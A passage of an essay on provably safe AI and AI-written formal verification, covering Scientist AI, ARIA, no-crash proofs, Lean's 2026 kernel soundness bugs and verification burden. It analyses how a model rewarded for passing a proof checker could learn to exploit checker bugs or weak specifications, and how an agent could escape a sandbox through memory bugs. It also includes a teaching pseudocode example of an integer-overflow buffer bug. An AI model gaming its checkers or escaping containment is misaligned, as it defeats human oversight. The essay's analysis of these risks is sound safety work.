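To define $R$, the paper groups the possible Predictors, before any training, by how well they score on the training objective. $R$ is the largest share of dangerous Predictors in any group, and $C$ is the most that training can multiply this share. If $R$ were one in a billion and $C$ were 1,000, the chance that training produces a dangerous Predictor would be at most one in a million. The paper argues that $R$ is small because a Predictor would have to make many coordinated errors to cause a disaster, and that $C$ is small because training doesn't reward such errors. It doesn't measure either number for a real system.

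The 2024 theorem also bounded the true chance of harm, whereas the new one measures danger by the posterior, which is the best estimate that the data and the prior support. Bengio and colleagues say their theorems don't settle whether this estimate recognises real hazards. An honest Predictor could still approve a dangerous flu sequence if its data contained too little about how flu viruses enter cells. Scientist AI is therefore mainly a way to stop a learned world model from being deceptive, not to prove that it is accurate. *AI Safety* (2026) proposes using the Predictor as one part of a larger system that also includes independent verification.

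LawZero still has to show that the method works. The 2026 paper sets out requirements for turning ordinary text into labelled statements, but not a complete algorithm. In an April 2026 interview with the podcast host Rob Wiblin, Bengio described plans to train small models from scratch and to adapt existing ones. Adapting a model would be quicker but lose the mathematical guarantees. LawZero had raised about $35 million, but a model that could compete with the leading ones would cost billions.

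### A common language for physical systems

ARIA now puts verified software first, but it also funds research on modelling physical systems. Ammann explains in the programme's May 2026 thesis that real systems mix several kinds of behaviour. In the tank, the temperature changes continuously, a safety switch is either on or off, and a sensor may fail at random. Engineers already have separate mathematical languages for these behaviours, such as differential equations and Markov processes. ARIA wants a single framework that can combine them.

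The framework should also handle probabilities that engineers know only to within a range, like the valve's failure rate in the second section. A specification could limit how much an action increases the risk of harm compared with doing nothing.

Certificates for physical systems include barrier functions, which show that a system can't cross from safe states into unsafe ones. The argument about the tank at 50 degrees is a simple example. For more complicated systems, researchers can train a neural network to act as the certificate, then use a separate checker to confirm it is valid.

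Many of these parts exist separately, but the shared framework is still a goal. Engineers use the individual modelling languages and barrier functions, runtime monitors are common, and researchers have published methods for learning certificates. By May 2026, ARIA had fully funded its work on tools, and the programme is due to end in late 2027. ARIA hopes the tools will include monitors that compare incoming observations with the formal model. As the tools improve, it hopes to extend its applications from cybersecurity to energy, transport and medical devices.

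Ammann says that researchers may have to verify consistency instead of correctness for subjects such as epidemics, climate and the economy. A proof might then show that the parts of an epidemic model agree with each other, but not that a real epidemic will stay within the model's limits. Her view on these subjects is close to Dickson's.

### Where the gap is small, and how to test it elsewhere

The gap between model and world is smallest where people build the system to match the model, as with software, computer chips and a synthesiser restricted to an approved list. It is also fairly small for machines with well-understood physics and a safe fallback, such as heated tanks and many parts of a power grid. It is largest where the outcome depends on living things or people's decisions.

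Hatfield-Dodds called guaranteed safe AI "vaporware" in his comment and said he would love to see a demonstration project. A convincing one could use a moderately difficult physical system, such as a town's heating network. The operators would publish the model and the proved bound in advance, then record every time the network did something the model excluded. To show with 95% confidence that such events happen less than once in 10,000 hours, they would need about 30,000 hours without one. That is nearly three and a half years at one site, or less than two weeks at 100 similar sites.

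A hostile team should also try to push the network outside what the model allows, since operators learn little about attacks from normal operation. The operators should report how many useful actions the gatekeeper refused, because a model that allows every possible outcome is never wrong but can't be used to prove that anything is safe.

For biology, the first test could be done entirely on computers. Researchers could give a cell-entry model the sequences of viruses known to infect humans, including some its designers had never studied. If the model classified even one as safe, it would not be a sound overapproximation. If it rejected them all and still accepted most harmless sequences, there would be much less reason to think that a useful safety check requires simulating a whole human body.

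## Whether proofs can be produced and trusted at the scale of modern AI

For decades, people usually left software unverified because verification took too much work. The best-known verified program, seL4, is an operating-system kernel, which controls access to memory and hardware. It has 8,700 lines of C code, and its proof took 20 person-years and is 200,000 lines long, according to *AI Could Make Formal Verification Economically Viable at Scale* (2025). At that rate, one person verifies about 435 lines of code a year, or two per working day. A program of a million lines would take 2,300 person-years, even if the work grew only in proportion to the program's length.

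seL4 was one of the verified components that withstood expert attackers in the American military programme HACMS, so its proofs were worth having. But such projects remained rare. CompCert, a verified C compiler, has proofs eight times as long as the compiler, and the effort of writing such proofs limits how much software anyone verifies, according to Dafny's *The Cost of Bugs and of Verification* (2025).

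A proof makes financial sense when it costs less than the losses it is likely to prevent. If a program has a 1% chance of containing a flaw that would cost its owner £1 million, a proof that rules out the flaw is worth about £10,000. At £100,000 per person-year, a proof like seL4's costs £2 million. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, argued that AI would change this calculation. He thought proofs were one of the best uses for a language model because its mistakes do little harm, since the checker rejects an invalid proof and the model has to try again.

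### From fuzz tests to theorems

Within a year, AI had made proofs about software much easier to produce. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a project with the formal-methods company Theorem in which Claude proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries. The libraries came from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that looks for bugs by fuzzing, which means running a program on huge numbers of unusual inputs to see whether anything goes wrong. Each fuzz test has an entry point, a small program that passes a string of bytes to part of a library.

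The team turned 239 of these tests into theorems about the compiled programs. A fuzz test covers only the inputs it tries, but for each program $b$, the theorem covers every input $x$ below a certain size:

$$\text{size}(x) < 64\text{ MB} \;\Rightarrow\; b \text{ exits normally on } x$$

EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) explains that the proofs rule out crashes, failed assertions (checks written into the code) and memory-safety errors, such as writing past the end of a buffer. There are more than $10^{150,000,000}$ inputs of this size, so fuzzing could never test them all.

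A small invented example shows how an attempted proof can find a bug that fuzzing misses:

```
read two 32-bit numbers, a and b, from the file
if a + b < 256:
    copy a bytes, then b bytes, into a 256-byte buffer
```

The code looks safe but isn't, because 32-bit addition starts again from zero after 4,294,967,295. If $a$ is 4,294,967,295 and $b$ is 2, the computer gets a sum of 1. The check passes, and the program tries to copy four billion bytes into the buffer. With random values of $a$ and $b$, only about one file in 17 million would get past the check. But a proof has to show that the true sum is at most 256, which doesn't follow from the check, so an AI that gets stuck at this step has found the bug.

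In a project that took a few weeks, Claude wrote about 180 million lines of proof (Smith, *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*, 2026), and Rocq's checker confirmed them. The Russian technology site OpenNET reports about 600,000 lines for a program of 18,000 machine instructions, or about 33 lines per instruction (*Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI*, 2026). Nobody will read proofs this long, but they don't need to be read if the checker and the specification are correct.

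Claude also found and fixed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed. One was in libexpat, a library for reading XML files, where certain inputs could overflow a buffer.

Two other results in the project concerned more than crashes. Claude proved that the Linux kernel's version of zlib, which compresses data, follows the published standard. It also wrote an interpreter for part of the Python language and proved that it matches a formal description of Python's behaviour. The team then ran 1.7 million random programs on both this interpreter and the standard one. The results matched for 99.95% of the programs, and the rest were known special cases. Python has no official formal definition, so only testing can check the description against the Python that people use.

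The no-crash theorems assume that each program runs as a single thread in a mathematical model of Linux on a RISC-V processor with a fixed amount of memory. They don't cover faulty hardware, code that a program loads while it runs, or parts of a library that the entry point never uses. Claude could not prove some of the targets, and Anthropic is publishing the specifications for those too.

A program that never crashes can still be useless. An image library that decoded every photograph as a black square would satisfy its theorem unless the fuzz test included an assertion about the decoded image.

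### Other processors and stronger properties

Most personal computers and servers use x86 processors, which are harder to model than RISC-V. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presented a proof covering everything a Linux process does as it runs one x86 program. Like Anthropic's proofs, it is about the compiled program, so nobody has to trust the compiler.

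In *AlphaProof Code* (November 2026), Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues proved much stronger properties of the code behind Signal, an encrypted messaging app. One was forward secrecy, which means an attacker who steals someone's current keys still can't read their earlier messages. Tegmark had said a year earlier that his group was working on verifying Signal. At Google, AI agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of Lean in four weeks.

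Those proofs depend on 26,000 lines of specifications and processor model that people have to trust, about three times the length of seL4's code. Stating that a conversation is secure takes many more definitions than stating that a program doesn't crash. To check that the theorems excluded real problems, the researchers put two old bugs back into test copies of the program and proved that each violated a theorem. But according to EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026), the work covers a small test program for one-to-one messages and leaves out key generation. The proofs therefore wouldn't protect messages from an attacker who could guess the keys.

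*Formalizing CPython* (Andrews and Zhang, 2026) takes a less rigorous approach to CPython, the program that runs almost all Python code. Claude agents copied its functions into Lean line by line, tested the copies against the originals, and proved theorems about the copies. A second agent has accepted 4,071 functions so far, and the project has covered about 16% of CPython. It has produced 418 bug reports, about 55 of which describe ways for ordinary Python code to crash the interpreter or corrupt memory. The method is very good at finding bugs, but it provides weaker evidence that CPython is correct than a proof about the compiled program would, because a copy can differ from the original in a case that nobody tested.

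### How often AI succeeds

In the 2025 talk *Provably Safe AI*, Tegmark gave success rates from a benchmark for "vericoding", in which a person writes a specification and an AI writes both the program and a proof that it meets the specification. The AI succeeded on 82% of tasks in Dafny, 44% in Rust and 27% in Lean. When it only had to prove that an existing program met its specification, the best rate was 96%, up from 68% a year earlier.

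Part of the gap between languages probably comes from how much of the proof each one automates. In Dafny, the programmer adds hints, such as loop invariants, and an automatic solver fills in the rest. The programmer has to supply much more of the proof in Lean.

The 27% figure for Lean is now badly out of date. In *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search*, Yao (2026) tested newer models on 423 of the benchmark's Lean specifications. Models from American companies did about as well as their predecessors when they worked in the original way, without extended reasoning, but far better as agents that could search Lean's mathematics library and keep revising their proofs. GPT-5.4 solved 95% with up to 50 model calls per task. Yao used only part of the Lean benchmark, so the two percentages are not exactly comparable, but that difference can't explain such a large improvement.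 Yao concludes that researchers need harder benchmarks based on modern code.

Results on real projects vary widely. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) describes using Claude to produce a 7,800-line proof about a compiler in about 96 hours, after a comparable proof had taken several months by hand. In April 2026, a developer on the programming-language project Fiducia spent about $3,000 and four days on a proof in the Rocq proof assistant. Claude kept writing proof scripts that almost worked, and five necessary lemmas remained unproved.

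The number of lines in a proof is a poor measure of progress, since AI can write long proofs cheaply. *Please measure verification burden* proposes reporting the verification burden, which is the cost of proving a program correct divided by the cost of writing it. If an AI uses £100 of tokens to write a program and £1,000 to prove it correct, the burden is 10. The post also proposes reporting how much the burden varies, because an average would hide cases like Fiducia's.

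### What "checked in Lean" means

In October 2026, OpenAI released 722 mathematics papers by an AI model, many with Lean code. The release made it urgent for mathematicians to know what such code proves. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), a post on a blog about Lean for mathematicians, recommends several checks before anyone relies on AI-written proofs.

According to the post, about 38 of the 290 papers with Lean code had code that didn't state the paper's main theorem. OpenAI had not claimed that it did, but a reader who saw only that Lean had accepted the code could easily have assumed so.

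A single wrong symbol can also keep a formal statement from matching its intended meaning. Fermat's Last Theorem is that $a^n + b^n = c^n$ has no solution in positive whole numbers when $n$ is at least 3. The statement becomes false if it is written in Lean for all natural numbers, because Lean counts 0 as a natural number and $0^3 + 0^3 = 0^3$. This mistake does little harm, since nobody can prove the false version in a working system. A statement that is too weak is more dangerous, because it is easier to prove than the intended one.

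Comparing the statements sometimes means reading thousands of lines. In September 2026, Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem* (2026) announced a computer-checked proof that took Claude 11 days, and that theorem can be stated in a line or two. But the statement in an AI-written proof of another famous result, the classification of finite simple groups, depends on about 5,600 lines of AI-written definitions. According to the Xena post, its author had not met anyone who claimed to have carefully checked the hardest of these definitions. Anyone who wants to rely on the Signal proofs faces the same problem with the 26,000 trusted lines behind them.

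A proof is much easier to check than to find, as Tegmark and Omohundro say, but checking a very long one can take more computing power than most people have. When the Xena author tried to check Claude's 13 million lines on Fermat's Last Theorem, his computer ran out of memory, and he succeeded only after Anthropic lent him a machine with 96 processor cores and 500 gigabytes of memory. He also put the code in a sandbox, because compiling AI-written Lean can run other code, which could delete files.

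Reviewers should also look for gaps in proofs. Lean lets an author write `sorry` in place of a missing proof, or add an axiom, a statement Lean accepts without proof. Both have legitimate uses in unfinished work. Lean can list every axiom a theorem depends on, including any use of `sorry`.

### Two bugs in Lean's checker

Even a complete proof of the right statement can't be trusted if the checker accepts false theorems. Lean's checker has a small core called the kernel. According to *Lean4Lean* (2024), no one ever reported a bug that let the kernel accept a false theorem in Lean 3, the previous major version. In July 2026, Lean's developers fixed two such bugs in the current version within a week.

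Patrick Hulin found a bug in Lean with help from GPT-5.6 Sol. According to Lean's release notes (2026), the bug could be exploited only by malicious code running in the same process as the kernel, and such code already had simpler ways to cheat. Lean's developers recommend checking suspicious proofs with a separate tool called comparator, on which this exploit would not have worked.

The other bug was more serious. On 25 July, Ramana Kumar published an apparent disproof of the Collatz conjecture, produced with AI assistance. The conjecture is that if you start with any positive whole number and repeatedly halve it when it is even, or triple it and add one when it is odd, you always reach 1. Lean accepted the disproof only because its kernel failed to check part of the definition of certain complicated data types.

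Three days later, Kiran Gopinathan reduced the disproof to a short proof of `False`, Lean's name for a contradiction. Any statement follows from a contradiction, so someone could have used the same trick to "prove" any program safe. Lean's developers released a fix an hour after his report, according to their August postmortem, which skybrian quotes in *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*.

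Comparator would not have caught this bug, because it relies on the same kernel. Nanoda, an independently written checker, didn't have the bug, but Machine Logic's *Why is it all in the kernel?* reports that the false disproof passed Nanoda too. Nanoda had a different bug, since fixed, and Lean's notes explain that Kumar had shown how a single proof could exploit both.

Independent checkers protect very well against honest mistakes, because two separately written programs are unlikely to make the same error on the same proof. They protect less well against an adversary, who can look for a flaw in each checker and write one proof that exploits them all, although each extra checker makes this harder.

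Another approach is to verify the checker. Lean4Lean is a checker for Lean, written in Lean, and the project aims to prove that it follows the rules of Lean's logic. This would remove most of the places where a coding mistake could go unnoticed, but people would still need another checker to confirm the proof.

Rocq, which checked Anthropic's 180 million lines, has had bugs of this kind too. None of this suggests that those proofs are wrong, but a checker's good record with honest users is weak evidence that it will withstand an AI that searches for flaws, and AI helped find both of the July bugs.

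### When passing the checker earns a reward

An AI might search for flaws because training that rewards it for passing a checker reinforces whatever the checker accepts.

A weak specification is the easiest thing to exploit. Lorica (2026), in *Maybe we've been thinking about verification backwards*, describes lean-zip, a data-compression program with a proof that decompression always recovers the original data. If $C$ compresses and $D$ decompresses, then for every $x$,

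$$D(C(x)) = x$$

Lorica suggests that proofs like this could speed up development, since an AI can rewrite the code freely as long as the theorem still holds. But a program that doesn't compress anything also satisfies this equation. If the equation were the whole specification, an AI rewarded for speed could return the data unchanged. Something similar happened with ordinary tests, when a coding agent abandoned the requirement to store data and produced a database that ran six times faster and still passed every test.

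The no-crash theorems have the same weakness wherever Claude changed the code, because Claude could have stopped a crash by deleting the feature that caused it. The proofs Anthropic is publishing don't have this weakness, because they are for programs that needed no changes.

Bugs in a proof checker are much rarer than weak specifications, but they are more useful to a model that cheats because exploiting one bug can work on every theorem. Suppose a model finds honest proofs for 30% of its training problems and happens to exploit such a bug once in 10,000 attempts. In a million attempts, it would use the exploit about 100 times and earn a reward every time. Since honest attempts succeed only 30% of the time, training would favour the exploit and might eventually make it the model's usual method.

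After fixing a checker, developers can rerun it on every stored proof and discard the ones that fail. RLHF has no equivalent, because nobody can recheck a large collection of human preferences this way. But rechecking may come too late if a gatekeeper has already let a program through, and it doesn't remove what the model learned.

### What cheap proofs change

The objection that verification takes too much labour no longer holds for a large class of ordinary software. As proofs become easier to produce, more of the difficulty lies in writing specifications and choosing models and assumptions, as Tolmach and Klaus (2026) argue in *The proof is in the spec*.

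This helps the case for verifying the software around an AI. An agent can escape from a sandbox through a memory-safety bug, and Claude has now proved the absence of such bugs in hundreds of compiled programs. Moon and Varshney had to exclude the operating system from their guarantee for a containment layer, but easier proofs could eventually let such a guarantee cover much of it. ARIA bet on progress like this when it moved from gatekeepers to verified software, and so far that looks like a good decision.

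However, the no-crash proofs assume a single thread, while a containment layer usually has to serve several agents at once. The proofs would not cover the payment wrapper that let two simultaneous £40 payments through.

The new proofs also don't help settle the dispute about the AI itself, because none of them verified a model's weights or aims. Engineers might use the same methods to prove that the program running a language model never crashes and does all its arithmetic correctly. The model could still write a blackmail threat, because the threat would be the correct result of that arithmetic. Verifying the network remains a separate and much harder problem.

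It would be more useful next to verify a complete containment layer that is in daily use and runs on several processor cores, along with the parts of the operating system it depends on. More lines of proof about more libraries would add little. One team should write the specification while another tries to cause harm without violating it. Independent checkers should confirm the proof, and the developers should publish the cost.

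They should then keep the proof up to date for a year as the software changes. If each update needs only a small addition to the proof, companies could treat verification as a normal part of software development. If they often have to start the proof again, many will probably run new code with an old proof.
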